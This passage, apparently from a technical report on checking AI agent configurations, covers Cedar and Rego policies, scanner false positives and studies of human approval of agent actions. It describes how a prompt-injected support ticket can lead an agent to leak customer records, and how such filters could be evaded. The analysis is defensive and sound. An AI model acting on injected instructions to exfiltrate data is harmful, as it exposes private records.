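The attacker's ticket can still cause the model to request record 1042. But `customer_id` comes from the login, which the model cannot alter, so it doesn't match 1042 and the gateway denies the request. The agent still has all three parts of the lethal trifecta, so a combination rule would still flag it, but an attacker can obtain only their own record through this tool.

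A program called Cedar Analysis translates these policies into formulas, as Zelkova does for IAM. It looks for several kinds of mistake:

- A rule that can never apply, such as one requiring a customer's tier to be both gold and platinum.
- A rule that always applies, such as one for orders of at least 100 items or fewer than 100.
- A "permit" rule that a "forbid" rule cancels completely.
- An edit that permits more than before. In AWS's example, the old rule blocked discounts on limited editions. The new one blocks them only for orders of more than 200, so an order for 73 now gets the discount.

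The last check is the most useful for reviewing changes to an agent, because people easily misread this kind of edit. Adding a condition usually makes a rule stricter, but here the condition is inside an exception, so it makes the rule looser.

These results are proofs about the policy, and AWS describes them as "mathematical certainty" that policies behave as intended. That goes too far, because the analysis doesn't include what anyone intended. Developers can write a rule in English and have a language model translate it into Cedar. If the model writes a refund limit of $1,000 instead of $100, the policy is still consistent and applies in some cases but not others, so none of the checks for logical errors would catch the mistake. Someone has to read the translated policy or compare it with a limit they wrote separately.

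The guarantee also depends on settings outside the policy. Trend Micro's *Configure Policy Engine for AgentCore Gateway* warns that without a policy engine attached, an agent can call any tool on the gateway. By default, AgentCore does not create a policy if the analyser finds a problem, but AWS lets users override this with `IGNORE_ALL_FINDINGS`. In `LOG_ONLY` mode, AgentCore records a policy's decisions but does not enforce them. A checker can read all of these settings and should do so before relying on any proof.

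The agent must also have no way around the gateway. Brooker (2026), an engineer at AWS, calls the gateway "the singular hole in the box" and says that the runtime, where the agent runs, blocks other traffic. An agent on a developer's laptop with its own shell and internet connection can bypass the gateway, so a proof about the gateway's policy covers little of what the agent can do.

### Rules about what happened earlier

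Cedar evaluates each request separately, so it cannot express the rule the shop most needs, which is that an agent must never make a web request after a customer lookup. In late July 2026, AWS released Dogwood, an extension of Cedar whose rules can refer to earlier tool calls. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) gives a nearly identical example, in which an agent should stop contacting outsiders once it has accessed confidential data.

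Cedar's analysis tools do not work on rules about history, which are easy to get wrong. InfoQ describes a $5,000 limit on transfers and an agent that requests three transfers of $2,000 at the same moment. A rule that adds up *completed* transfers permits all three, because none has completed yet. A rule that adds up *requested* transfers stops the third. None of AWS's tools can prove which rule enforces the limit.

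According to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*, these rules consider earlier actions within one conversation. If the shop's agent saves a customer's record in its memory on Monday and sends it out in a new conversation on Tuesday, the rule can't use Monday's lookup to block the request. A static rule that limits `http_get` to the delivery companies' sites applies in every conversation, and Cedar Analysis can check it.

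Dogwood rules can also use scores from AWS's content filters, for example to refuse a call that looks like part of a prompt injection. The gateway applies the score threshold reliably, but the score is only a classifier's estimate, so an attacker who finds wording that scores low will get past the rule.

### Provers that look for combinations

NVIDIA has built a prover that checks whether an agent's permissions together would let it steal data, which none of the Cedar checks described so far does. The prover is for OpenShell, NVIDIA's software for running agents in sandboxes. *What we have learned applying formal methods to control AI agents* (Watson, 2026) presents it as a continuation of AWS's work on IAM policies. The prover uses Z3 to search a sandbox's policy for ways to send data out, ways around a ban on writing, and chains of programs that together give an agent more power than it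 should have. Watson reported seven small test cases with the code. All passed, but they don't show how many false alarms the prover raises on real agents. In November 2026, OpenShell adopted Cedar as its policy language. One reason, according to *Cedar as the policy language in OpenShell* (Raman, 2026), is that comparing two Cedar policies is decidable, so a program can always determine whether a change gives an agent more access.

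AWS announced its own version, Greenlight, on 1 December 2026, and so far offers it only as a preview. Greenlight denies access to all tools and network destinations by default, and a language model drafts rules from a company's documents and records of past tool calls. *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports that Greenlight then uses automated reasoning to find conflicting rules and paths to resources outside the agent's approved access. *AWS Greenlight Gives Partners A Go At AI Agent Governance* (Millward, 2026) adds that Greenlight looks for combinations of access that could lead to an unintended action.

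*AWS greenlights autonomous AI agents to take control* (Wheatley, 2026) reports AWS's claim that such reasoning proves or disproves statements with 100% certainty, so companies need to test each rule only once. The claim is reasonable for a fixed rule and a fixed set of tools, but it no longer holds when someone adds a tool, widens a token's access or connects a second agent. Pogorelec reports that AWS still plans to add support for systems of several agents.

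## False positives and adoption: the record of infrastructure scanners

A correct finding protects nobody if the recipient dismisses it as a false alarm. People use "false positive" for several situations, each of which calls for a different remedy. Suppose a checker warns the shop that its support agent can send customer records to any website.

| Why the alarm counts as false | What this could look like at the shop | What would help |
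|---|---|---|
| The reported fact is wrong | A firewall that the checker did not read already limits the agent to the delivery companies' sites | A checker that reads more of the settings |
| The fact is right but harmless here | `lookup_customer` connects to a test database of invented customers | Information about what the database holds |
| The risk is real but accepted | The owner knows that a ticket could steal a record, but wants unrestricted parcel tracking until the Christmas rush is over | A record of the decision |
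| The developer takes no action | The message says only "TF001", and the developer closes it without understanding it | A clearer message |

The last row is Google's definition, from *Lessons from Building Static Analysis Tools at Google* (Sadowski, Aftandilian and colleagues, 2018). A finding is an "effective false positive" if developers saw it and took no positive action. This includes true findings that nobody understood, but not wrong findings that still led a developer to improve the code. For example, the shop's developer might narrow `allowedHosts` although the firewall already blocked every other host. The alarm was wrong but useful, because the agent will stay safe if someone later changes the firewall.

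A scanner's precision can depend heavily on how false positives are defined. Suppose a scanner raises 100 alarms. In 20 of them the reported fact is wrong, in 25 it is harmless, and in 15 the owner has accepted the risk. Developers fix 24 of the remaining 40 and do nothing about the other 76 alarms. The scanner's precision is 80% if only wrong facts count as false positives, 55% if harmless facts count too, and 40% if accepted risks also count. It is 24% by Google's definition, which counts every alarm that developers don't act on as a false positive.

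Company records often mix up false alarms with real findings that developers chose not to fix. *Secrets That Survive Everything* (2026), a study of web applications, describes keys that must be present in the user's browser, such as those for Google Maps, and that scanners report as leaked secrets. The developer knows the key is real but considers the exposure a normal part of the design, or lacks the time or authority to build a server that would hide it. So the developer dismisses the alert as a false positive or adds the key to an ignore list, and scanners no longer monitor it. Counting dismissed alerts as false positives therefore overstates how often the scanner was wrong.

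### Infrastructure as code

Scanners for agents are too new to have much of a track record, but scanners for infrastructure as code have done a similar job for years. Infrastructure as code means describing servers, networks and user accounts in scripts, which tools such as Terraform, Puppet, Ansible and Chef use to set them up automatically. *A Different Kind of Smell* (Rahman and Williams, 2020) gives the example of the Intercontinental Exchange, which manages 75% of its 20,000 servers with such scripts. It cut the time needed to set up a development environment from a day or two to 21 minutes, but a mistake in a script spreads just as quickly.

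The scanners read these scripts before anyone runs them and report dangerous settings. Three well-known open-source scanners are Checkov from Palo Alto Networks, KICS from Checkmarx and Trivy from Aqua Security. *A Comparison of Kubernetes Compliance Standards and Configuration Scanners* (2026) lists more than 110 checks for Checkov, 140 for KICS and 160 for Trivy. The paper examines them as scanners for Kubernetes, which runs programs in containers across many machines, but all three also read other kinds of file.

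Three lines of Puppet show why these scanners raise disputed alarms:

```puppet
$user      = "admin"
$bind_host = "0.0.0.0"
$apturl    = "http://deb.debian.org/debian"
```

A simple scanner flags all three lines of the script. The first gives a program an administrator's name, the second accepts connections from any address, and the third downloads software without encryption. The scanner identifies all of this correctly, but its results don't show whether any of the lines matters. A mail server has to accept connections from anywhere, but a database server should not, and the script may not show which one it sets up. The download address belongs to Debian, a well-known source of free software.

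### A thousand bug reports

The best-known study of such mistakes is by Rahman, Parnin and Williams (2019), in *The Seven Sins*. They read 1,726 scripts by hand and looked for "security smells", recurring patterns that suggest a weakness. They found seven:

- administrator rights by default
- empty passwords
- secrets written into the script
- servers open to every address
- comments that reveal unfinished or faulty work
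- web connections without encryption
- weak cryptography

They then wrote SLIC, a linter (a program that searches code for suspicious patterns), and ran it on 15,232 scripts from 293 open-source repositories. It reported 21,201 smells, including 1,326 passwords.

A smell is a reason to look more closely, not a proven vulnerability. Rahman and Williams explain that a password in a script matters only if something uses it to log in, and SLIC does not check whether anything does.

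To learn what developers thought of the smells, Rahman and colleagues picked 1,000 at random and filed a bug report for each. Developers responded to 212 reports and agreed to fix 148 of the smells, which is 70% of the responses but only 15% of the reports. Nobody knows what the developers who didn't respond thought, or whether they read the reports. If they had all agreed, the share of reports would be 94%.

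Many smells stay in place for a long time. Secrets had a median lifetime of 20 months, and one lasted 98 months. *Security smells in infrastructure as code* (War, 2025) also found that smells persist for long periods in GitHub projects, and suggests that inadequate tools are the likely reason. Alternatively, the owners may have known about the smells and not minded.

Rahman and Williams report a later round, with 500 reports each for Puppet, Ansible and Chef scripts. Developers gave an opinion on 187 of the 1,500 smells and agreed with about 64% of those. One admitted being "a bit sloppy" about an unencrypted download. Those who disagreed mostly pointed to the context, such as a password that appeared only in a test or an unencrypted connection that never left the machine ("It's using http on localhost, what's the risk?").

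Rahman and Williams see a lack of security awareness in these answers, because another programmer may copy the script and use it where the setting is dangerous. This does happen, but the bug report asked the developer about a risk in this project, and the developer probably answered correctly.

### One linter, several precision figures

SLIC's developers originally measured its precision at 99%. In *Leveraging Practitioners' Feedback to Improve a Security Linter*, Reis, Abreu and colleagues (2022) retested it on new Puppet scripts and then built an improved linter called InfraSecure. The results depend heavily on who judged the warnings.

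| Linter | Who judged | Warnings judged | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| SLIC | Its developers' published test | 58 | 99% |
| SLIC | Two of Reis's co-authors, sample in proportion to each type of warning | 250 | 64% |
| SLIC | The same two, equal numbers of each type | 252 | 55% |
| SLIC | Owners of the projects | 298 | 28% |
| InfraSecure, first version | The two co-authors, on the proportional sample | 193 | 76% |
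| InfraSecure, final version | 131 practitioners | 309 | 83% |

The co-authors were PhD students who didn't know the projects. The project owners judged the warnings much more harshly, accepting only one of 73 about unencrypted connections and 77 of 196 about secrets.

The 28% is less solid than it would be if owners had judged each warning separately. Reis and colleagues combined the warnings of one type in a project into a single report, about nine on average, so one reply of "All false positives" could reject many warnings at once. They filed 228 reports and received only 33 clear answers. Rahman and Williams, who filed a separate report for each smell, found that owners of Puppet projects agreed with 63% of the 104 smells they responded to. The two studies also chose different projects and counted answers differently, so no single factor explains the gap. In both studies, owners rejected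 far more than 1% of the warnings.

Many of SLIC's mistakes came from matching text regardless of how the text was used. It reported weak cryptography whenever it found the letters "md5", even in the name of a checksum, which only verifies that a file has arrived intact. It flagged a variable called `aws_admin_username` as a secret, although the value was the name of the operating system. Usernames made up 48% of the secrets it reported, and practitioners did not consider a username without a password a threat.

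InfraSecure checks whether a line assigns a fixed value, and ignores placeholders and publicly documented default accounts. It also lets a company list sites that may use unencrypted connections, and turn off the check for usernames separately. The first version, which had only some of these changes, cut false warnings on the proportional sample from 91 to 46, but also removed 12 of the 159 correct ones, or roughly 8%. That seems a good trade-off for a linter, though a security team would want to know what the 12 lost warnings were.

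The rise from 64% to 76%, with the same judges and the same sample, is better evidence that the feedback helped than the overall increase in precision from 28% to 83% that Reis and colleagues describe. The 28% comes from owners judging the old linter, and the 83% from strangers judging the new one. Only 14 of the 131 practitioners came from Puppet's online communities. The rest were paid participants from Prolific, a recruitment site, and were screened for relevant experience. Each participant saw a few lines of code and an explanation of the problem, and could not know whether the server was a test machine. The 83% also leaves out 34 answers of "I'm not sure", and would fall to 74% if those were counted as wrong.

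When Reis and colleagues later reported InfraSecure's warnings to owners of active projects, two replied that the issues were irrelevant because their applications were not in production, an objection that better pattern matching could not have prevented.

### When experts disagree

Precision is hard to measure if experts disagree about which findings are correct. *Do Experts Agree About Smelly Infrastructure?* (Masoumzadeh, Saavedra and colleagues, 2025) examines the labels behind GLITCH, another scanner for security smells. Three people had independently inspected each script, and the majority decided each label. One of the three had dissented on 46.3% of the smells, compared with 1.6% for smells in ordinary program code. The disagreements were not due to any single inspector, and they were especially common for administrator rights, empty passwords and secrets.

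A scanner tested against labels decided by a vote among inspectors can be marked wrong for agreeing with the minority. In 46.4% of GLITCH's false alarms, at least one of the three inspectors had also seen a problem in the same line, though not always the same problem. The other 53.6% were mistakes, since all three inspectors agreed that there was no smell.

The same doubt applies to agents, because whether a tool "reads private data" is at least as much a matter of judgement as whether a password is a secret. The MCP-SEC study also settled its disputed capability labels by majority vote. If a study of agent scanners published the split votes, readers could see how much of the error rate comes from disagreement among labellers.

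Comparing scanners with each other does not remove the need for human judges. *Compared to What?* (2026) ran Checkov, Trivy and KICS on 1,196 templates written by language models and 634 written by people, and measured the total number of findings from all three scanners per resource, such as a server or a storage area. Using the same scanners on both groups makes the comparison fairer, because a badly chosen rule affects both. But the measure doesn't show whether the findings are correct, and it counts a fault three times if all three scanners detect it. Agreement between scanners would also be weak evidence of a real risk, because they can all lack the same information about what a server is for.

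### Fixes that satisfy only the scanner

Counting fixes is an imperfect way around the argument over labels. A developer who changes the code has presumably taken the finding seriously, but language models now write many of these fixes, and a fix can remove the warning without removing the risk. *TerraProbe* (2026) calls these "deceptive fixes". For example, an asterisk in a policy can give access to every resource, and Checkov may flag it in one position but not in a neighbouring one. A model can then pass the check by moving the asterisk, which leaves the policy as permissive as before.

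Scanner findings can also be hard to fix properly. In *Security-First Evaluation of Text-to-Terraform* (2026), models wrote Terraform files, received the raw output of Checkov and Trivy, and tried again. Claude Opus 4, by now an old model, raised its compliance with Checkov's rules from 8.5% to 20.8%. The study attributes the modest gain to the type of repair needed to meet those rules, such as adding encryption or logging, which often requires a decision about the whole design. Newer models would probably do better, but they would still need to know what the company wants.

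At the shop, a model told to clear the alarm could delete `http_get` and give the agent a shell instead. If the checker's registry has no label for the shell, the alarm disappears even though the agent is now more dangerous. Rerunning the whole check after a fix helps only if the labels cover the replacement.

### Language models as filters

Researchers also use language models to sort real warnings from false ones after an ordinary scanner has run. The published scores need careful reading, because they depend on the mix of warnings in the test. *Beyond Benchmarks* (2026) gives the example of a test in which about 85% of the warnings were worth acting on. A filter that simply kept everything would have a precision of 85% and a recall of 100%. The usual combined score, F1, would then be

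F1 = 2 × 0.85 × 1 / (0.85 + 1) ≈ 0.92

This looks excellent for a filter that has removed nothing.

A sample of mostly false warnings is just as misleading. *Beyond Benchmarks* also describes a test of another filter on real C and C++ projects. Two experts reviewed 50 warnings, found 43 to be false and could not decide about the other seven. The filter removed 37 of the 43, or 86%, but a filter that deleted every warning would have scored 100%. Because the sample contained no confirmed real problems, the test could not show whether the filter removes those as well.

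Results can also drop sharply outside a benchmark. *ZeroFalse* (2025) reports that its method generally removed false alarms and kept most of the real alerts, but Gemini 2.5 Pro reached an F1 of only 0.372 on real-world code. That model is well over a year old, so its score is weak evidence of how current models perform.

*The Hitchhiker's Guide to Program Analysis, Part III* (2026) takes a more cautious approach. The model writes a small test program around the suspicious code so that a precise but slow analyser can examine that part alone, but the model doesn't decide whether the warning is real. The test set contained 200 warnings from Android drivers, of which 40 were real bugs. Depending on the model, the method removed between 48.8% and 63.8% of the 160 false alarms and kept the real bugs. Real bugs then made up between 33% and 41% of the list, up from 20%, so most of the remaining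 warnings were still false.

This caution matters more for an agent scanner than for a scanner of Android drivers. The filter would read tool descriptions, and an attacker can write a malicious tool's description to make the filter classify the tool as harmless. Using a model only to gather evidence, such as who owns a repository, and fixed rules to reach the verdict would limit the damage.

### Overnight reports and code review

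Whether developers act on a tool's reports depends on more than accuracy. *Scaling Static Analyses at Facebook* (Distefano et al., 2019) describes how the company introduced Infer, a program that looks for crashes and other errors. At first, Infer ran every night on the whole Android app. The team went through the results and assigned 20 to 30 issues to the developers who seemed best placed to fix them. They got almost no response, although they believed fewer than 20% of the reports were false.

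They then ran the same analysis whenever a developer submitted a change, and posted the results as comments in the code review, where colleagues discuss the change before accepting it. The share of issues that developers fixed rose to over 70%. Developers gave two reasons. They were already thinking about the code during a review, while an overnight report interrupted other work. The comment also reached the person who had just caused the problem, whereas an old issue might belong to someone who had left the company.

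This was not a controlled experiment, and the issues differed because the overnight run covered old code, while the comments in review covered only new problems. A survey at Google suggests that this difference matters. Developers there considered 74% of the issues that appeared while they were compiling new code to be "real problems", compared with 21% of those in code already in use. Sadowski and colleagues explain that testing and review have usually caught the serious errors by the time code has been in use for a while. Some of Facebook's improvement may therefore have come from showing developers issues that mattered more, though this is unlikely to explain the whole jump from near zero to 70%.

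At Google, showing a scanner's warnings during code review was not enough to make developers trust it. In 2006 Google began running FindBugs, a scanner for Java, every night and showing the results on a dashboard, which few people used. In 2009 hundreds of engineers spent a week going through the warnings. They reviewed 3,954, filed bug reports for 1,746, and fixed 640, or 16% of those reviewed. Google then put the warnings into code review, as Facebook would later do. It stopped doing so in 2011, partly because effective false positives had led developers to lose trust in the tool.

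Google set strict limits on false positives in the replacement. A check can now stop code from compiling only if it has no effective false positives and the problems it finds are easy to fix. Checks that run during code review may have up to 10% effective false positives. Each comment has a "Not useful" button, and if too many people press it, Google switches the check off until its author improves it. In January 2018, reviewers clicked "Please fix" more than 5,000 times a day, while "Not useful" received 250 clicks a day.

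Some of those complaints were about correct findings. One check warned about the wrong number of values in a formatted message, and about once a week somebody reported the warning as a mistake. The check was right every time, because the function accepted only one kind of placeholder and the developers had used another. Google added this explanation to the warning, and the complaints stopped.

Coverity, which sells a bug-finding program, similarly found that customers began to ignore the program, including its correct reports, when more than about 30% of the reports were false. Customers also labelled true reports false when they didn't understand them, which lowered their trust further. Coverity aimed for less than 20% false reports and dropped some checks that worked but were too difficult to explain. The first few reports mattered most, because a customer who saw three false ones in a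 row tended to give up.

Customers also disliked changes in the results. At one company the program found about 2,400 errors, and the staff fixed half of them. After an upgrade it found 3,600. The manager was furious, because the better scanner seemed to have undone the team's work. Coverity then tried to change less than 5% of its reported errors from one version to the next, and avoided any method with a random element.

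### Which lessons fit agents

Combination rules are well suited to reporting a problem when someone causes it, because an agent often becomes dangerous at a definite moment. For example, a developer might add `http_get` for parcel tracking to an agent that already has `read_ticket` and `lookup_customer`. A comment on that change could list the three tools and suggest limiting the hosts `http_get` can reach. But that developer may not be responsible for the customer database, so the comment may also have to reach its owner. Many agents are never reviewed because their settings are in a file on someone's laptop, and when a remote server adds a tool, there is no change to review.

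Warnings from regular scans of existing agents also deserve more attention than Google's old warnings did. A faulty line of Java that has run for three years without trouble is probably not very serious. But an agent that could leak customer records works normally until somebody attacks it, so its age is no evidence of safety. So an agent's owner should not ignore old problems, though Coverity's customers could reasonably fix only new bugs.

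Google's 10% limit would exclude today's agent scanners from its code reviews if effective false positives are at least as common as wrong findings. By its developers' count, 27% of AgentFlow's findings were wrong, as were about 37% of those from Agent Audit's MCP rules. But the limit may be stricter than necessary for agent configurations. Google analysed about 50,000 changes a day, while a company with 200 agents might have a few dozen findings in total. Facebook also accepts more false alarms when a missed problem could expose users' data. A security team can probably tolerate one wrong finding in three if each takes ten minutes to settle, but a developer who sees one wrong finding a year may not trust the next finding.

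Facebook's scanner Zoncolan serves both security engineers and developers. Of these programs, it is the most similar to an agent scanner, because it follows untrusted data through the website's code to sensitive operations. Security engineers see all its alarms on a dashboard. When a type of alarm has proved reliable, Facebook also turns it on for code review of new changes, where an engineer on duty checks the alarms first. Only the most reliable types go straight to the developer as comments. About a third of the types had reached code review by 2019, and people acted on close to 80% of the reports. In six months, Zoncolan stopped 211 severe problems in new changes and found 122 in existing code.

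Agent scanners could copy this arrangement with little change. At first, a team could show developers only the alarms about agents that read messages from strangers and can contact any host, until the capability labels for other tools have proved accurate.

The "Not useful" button would be harder to copy. A rule that fires ten times a year produces little feedback. Even if owners reject 30% of its findings in the long run, there is about a 15% chance that they reject at most one of the first ten. A vendor could pool answers from many customers if they agree to share them. The answers are also less informative than they were at Google, where a developer could often see from the code that a report was right. An owner who wrongly dismisses a toxic flow may never find out, because the theft leaves the agent working normally.

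Coverity's trouble with changing results is likely to be worse for agent scanners. Many of them get their capability labels from a language model, which may label the same tool differently after an update or from one run to the next. If a finding disappears when nobody has changed the agent, it looks like a false alarm even if it was correct. A scanner can avoid this by storing each label with a fingerprint of the tool's description and relabeling the tool only when the description changes. The scanner's makers should also announce when a new version changes old labels, so that owners can tell whether a new finding comes from a change to the agent or a change in labeling.

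### How many companies use agent scanners

Little is known about adoption. In November 2025, Thoughtworks' *Toxic flow analysis for AI* (2025) rated the method "Assess" in the Technology Radar, the software consultancy's regular review of new techniques. Thoughtworks uses this rating for ideas it considers worth exploring, and it described toxic flow analysis as "still in its early stages". Since then Snyk has extended its scanner, and NVIDIA and AWS have presented provers that look for dangerous combinations. This shows that vendors expect demand, but not how many companies run such checks or what they do with the results.

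Evaluations of agent scanners so far mostly measure whether findings are correct, and rarely whether anyone acts on them. The closest thing to a fix rate is the share of maintainers who accepted or fixed TaintAWI's findings, which excludes those who didn't reply. There don't seem to be published figures on how often owners suppress a toxic flow finding, how long a dangerous combination stays in place after the warning, or whether two agent scanners flag the same agents. No one has repeated Facebook's comparison with agents either. A company with a few hundred agents could do so by showing half its teams the findings when they change a configuration, sending the other half a weekly list, and counting how many agents in each group still have the combination after three months.

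## Turning a finding into a deployment decision

After a check produces a finding, someone still has to decide whether the agent may launch. A company with 200 agents will want identical configurations to get the same decision every time. It can do this with policy as code, which means writing rules about permitted configurations so that a program can enforce them automatically.

Open Policy Agent (OPA), an open-source program unrelated to AI agents despite its name, makes decisions and leaves their enforcement to other programs. Another program sends OPA structured data, such as a settings file. OPA checks the data against rules written in a language called Rego and returns a verdict, and the other program acts on it. Conftest is a small utility that runs Rego rules on configuration files.

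To judge the shop's support agent, the policy needs the capability labels, which can come from a second file:

```yaml
labels:
  read_ticket: [untrusted]
  lookup_customer: [private]
  http_get: [untrusted, outbound]
```

The policy itself is short:

```rego
package main

all_three := {"untrusted", "private", "outbound"}

# Collect the agent's labels. A tool without an entry gets all three.
held contains label if {
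  some server in input.mcpServers
  some tool in server.tools
  some label in object.get(data.labels, tool, all_three)
  not blocked(server, label)
}

# Ignore "outbound" if the server lists its hosts and none is "*".
blocked(server, "outbound") if {
  hosts := server.allowedHosts
  not "*" in hosts
}

deny contains msg if {
  count(all_three - held) == 0
  msg := "Untrusted text, private data and an open route out"
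}

deny contains "No capability labels loaded" if not data.labels
```

Here `input` is the shop's settings file and `data.labels` is the label file. A rule fires only if every line in its body holds. The asterisk in the list of hosts means `http_get` keeps its "outbound" label, so no label is missing and the first `deny` rule fires. Conftest prints the message and returns an exit code of 1, which signals a build system to stop. If the shop lists only the delivery companies' sites, `http_get` loses the "outbound" label and the file passes.

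The last line of the policy prevents every agent from passing if someone forgets to supply the label file. Without it, they would pass because Rego treats a reference to a missing value as "undefined", and a rule that depends on that value silently fails to fire. The policy would still pass a settings file that spells `mcpServers` differently, and one that allows `*.com`. Conftest can also run tests of the policy itself, so it is sensible to keep the shop's original file as a test case that the policy must refuse.

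### Where the policy can run

The same rules can run at several points before an agent starts work.

| Where | What starts the check | What this point offers |
|---|---|---|
| Editor | The developer, while writing the settings | The quickest answer, though the developer can skip it |
| Code review | A proposed change to the settings | A comment that colleagues can see |
| Deployment | A request to install the agent on company servers | A check on settings that nobody reviewed |
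| Agent start | The launch itself | The tools that the servers offer at that moment |

OPA has plugins for code editors, and Conftest's *Options* includes a ready-made GitHub workflow that checks each pull request. Conftest can also combine several files into one input, so a rule can compare an agent's tools with network rules that another team keeps elsewhere.

*Semantic Quorum Assurance* (2026) describes OPA's wide use in Kubernetes, where it can reject a request before the system stores it. OPA is good at structural questions, such as whether a service is open to the public, but weaker on questions of intent, such as whether deleting a folder is safe because a backup exists. Whether a configuration has the trifecta is mostly a structural question once the labels are right.

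OPA can also run checks after launch. *Trusted AI Agents in the Cloud* (2025) presents Omega, a platform that translates its policies into Rego and uses OPA to check the messages agents send to tools and to each other.

### How Bernstein refuses to start an agent

Bernstein, the program that coordinates coding agents and labels their tools by hand, checks each agent's configuration before launching it. It combines the labels of all the configured tools and refuses to launch the agent if the result is the full trifecta. Because the check runs before the agent's process exists, text that the agent reads cannot affect the result. Bernstein's "bypass" mode relaxes many other rules but not this one. Bernstein records the tools and labels involved in each refusal.

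An administrator can still weaken the check through a separate setting with three values: `enforce`, `warn` and `off`. The documentation recommends `warn` while a company is trying out unfamiliar tools and `enforce` in production.

According to Bernstein's documentation, the check ignores the arguments of a tool call and can't detect network traffic that an agent sends outside its declared tools, so the documentation recommends adding a sandbox. Another gap may be that label files in the project's own folder override the ones that come with Bernstein. An agent that can write to that folder could perhaps relabel a tool before the next agent starts, so the label files need the same protection as the settings.

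### Dropping a tool

Suppose the policy has refused the support agent and its owner wants to repair it. A repair works only if it actually removes one of the three conditions.

| Repair | Condition it removes | What can undo it |
|---|---|---|
| Drop a tool | Any condition that only this tool supplied | Another tool that supplies the same condition |
| Restrict destinations | The outbound channel to the attacker | An allowed site that accepts the attacker's content |
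| Split the agent | One condition from each part | Memory or files that the parts share |
| Require human approval | None | A person who approves the wrong call |

Removing a tool is the most dependable fix. If the shop removes `http_get` and no other tool can send data out, the theft fails whatever the ticket says. The tool's credential should be removed too. If the shop removes `lookup_customer` but leaves the database token where a shell can read it, the agent can still query the customer table.

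The shop can keep parcel tracking by replacing `http_get` with a tool that accepts only a parcel number and looks it up with the right delivery company. The model then can't compose a web address, and the tool can reject anything that doesn't look like a parcel number.

### Restricting destinations

A list of allowed hosts removes the outbound channel only if an attacker can't receive data through any host on the list. Docker's *Policies* warns that allowing `github.com` gives an agent access to everything on that site, including what its users post. An attacker can open an account there. PromptArmor's *what domains should i add to my allowlist* makes the same point about sites that host forms or rent out storage. A rule that permits every address at a cloud provider also permits any storage an attacker rents from that provider.

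The delivery companies' sites are a much better choice, but the shop should check them too. If one lets anyone add a note to a parcel through a web address, an attacker expecting a parcel could read the note.

Some controls restrict more than which sites an agent can contact. Anthropic's hosted version of Claude Code sends its GitHub traffic through a proxy that, according to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, checks that the agent is pushing only to the configured branch. This is far narrower than permission to contact `github.com`, but anyone who can read the branch can still read what the agent puts there.

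A checker also has to confirm that something enforces the list. Anthropic's *Sandboxing* describes a sandbox for the shell commands that Claude Code runs on a developer's computer. Its proxy decides by the name of the host that a program requests and doesn't inspect encrypted traffic, so a program may be able to disguise its real destination. Several settings determine how much protection the sandbox gives:

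- By default, if the sandbox can't start, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without it. Setting `failIfUnavailable` to true turns this into an error.
- A command that fails inside the sandbox may run outside it if the user agrees. Setting `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to false removes this option.
- Users can approve new sites when a prompt appears, unless an administrator has set `allowManagedDomainsOnly`.

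A rule that checks only for `"enabled": true` would accept a sandbox that may not be running. All three settings are easy to test in Rego.

### Splitting the agent

The shop could give `read_ticket` and `lookup_customer` to one agent and `http_get` to another. This helps only if the customer's record can't reach the agent with web access, whether through a message or a shared folder, database or memory.

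*Runtime Governance for AI Agents* (Kaptein, Khan and Podstavnychy, 2026) gives an example from finance. A bank keeps its advisers and traders apart so that traders don't learn about pending deals. An advising agent reads confidential deal data and then delegates a task to a trading agent. Each agent stays within its own permissions, yet the exchange can breach the barrier between advisers and traders.

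To be cautious, a checker can treat agents that share a writable store as one agent. This will flag some harmless divisions of capabilities between agents, and the owner can clear the finding by giving each agent its own store.

### Human approval

Requiring approval leaves all three conditions in place and adds a check on the path. This is attractive because the agent keeps all its abilities, but the measurements suggest that the check is weak.

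*Humans missed 1 in 3 threats approving AI agent commands* (Wauters, 2026) reports results from a browser game in which players approve or deny a coding agent's commands against the clock. Across over 40,000 runs and 409,000 decisions, the average player missed about one threat in three.

| Type of threat | Share missed |
|---|---|
| Openly destructive, such as deleting the whole disk | 11.7% |
| Lasting changes, such as a new scheduled task | 23.8% |
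| Sending data out or running unknown code | 33.4% |
| Reading files outside the task, such as cloud credentials | 35.0% |

Players were worst at spotting `npm run analyze`, a command that runs whatever script the project has named "analyze". They approved it 64.7% of the time, although the log just above the prompt showed that the script sent data to an outside address. They also blocked many safe commands, including 45% of requests to clear out old build files. Only 20.8% of players caught every threat while blocking at most a fifth of the safe commands.

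Wauters warns that this was a game with a time limit, that players knew it was a test, and that about 34% of the commands were threats. Real threats are rare, so people at work have less reason to expect one, but they also don't have to decide within seconds.

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports a much worse result from a more realistic experiment, in which only 13.6% of paid testers refused a dangerous command. The testers were doing coding tasks, didn't know which behaviour the study was measuring, and saw only one such command. They refused about 17% of the time early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls this approval fatigue, where people stop looking closely at what they approve.

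Anthropic ran the study to support a product that replaces the prompts. The testers were not protecting their own code or data, and they might have been more careful at work. But neither fact easily explains a drop from 17% to 5% within the same study.

Developers' own accounts support this. In *From Delegation to Action Approval*, Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. They found that 64% often approved at least one type of action without close review, as did 61% of those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code. The most common type was access to the internet, outside services or connected tools, at 36%, which is the step that completes the theft in the shop. The sample was not representative and people may misjudge their own habits, though they seem more likely to overstate their care than understate it.

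Training may not help much either. In the same survey, 70% of developers who knew of a security or privacy problem with agents often approved something without close review, compared with 43% of developers who knew of none. The gap remained after Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, which matters because heavy users may both hear of more problems and approve more actions.

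Even an attentive person may lack the information to judge an approval prompt. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) notes that an action can be acceptable alone and still complete something the user had forbidden. A prompt about a delivery site doesn't show that the agent has just read a customer's record. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) reports that most approval prompts in real products show only the raw command on a single line. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 reports the user had switched on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative.

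If the shop uses approval prompts, it should show fewer of them and include more information in each. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans the agent presents but only 3% of individual permission requests. They may reject plans for reasons unrelated to safety, but they are evidently reading them. The shop could ask for approval only before the agent contacts a new site, and say whose record the agent has read. A checker should keep the finding, because the trifecta is still complete, and list the approval as a guard.

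### Exceptions and old findings

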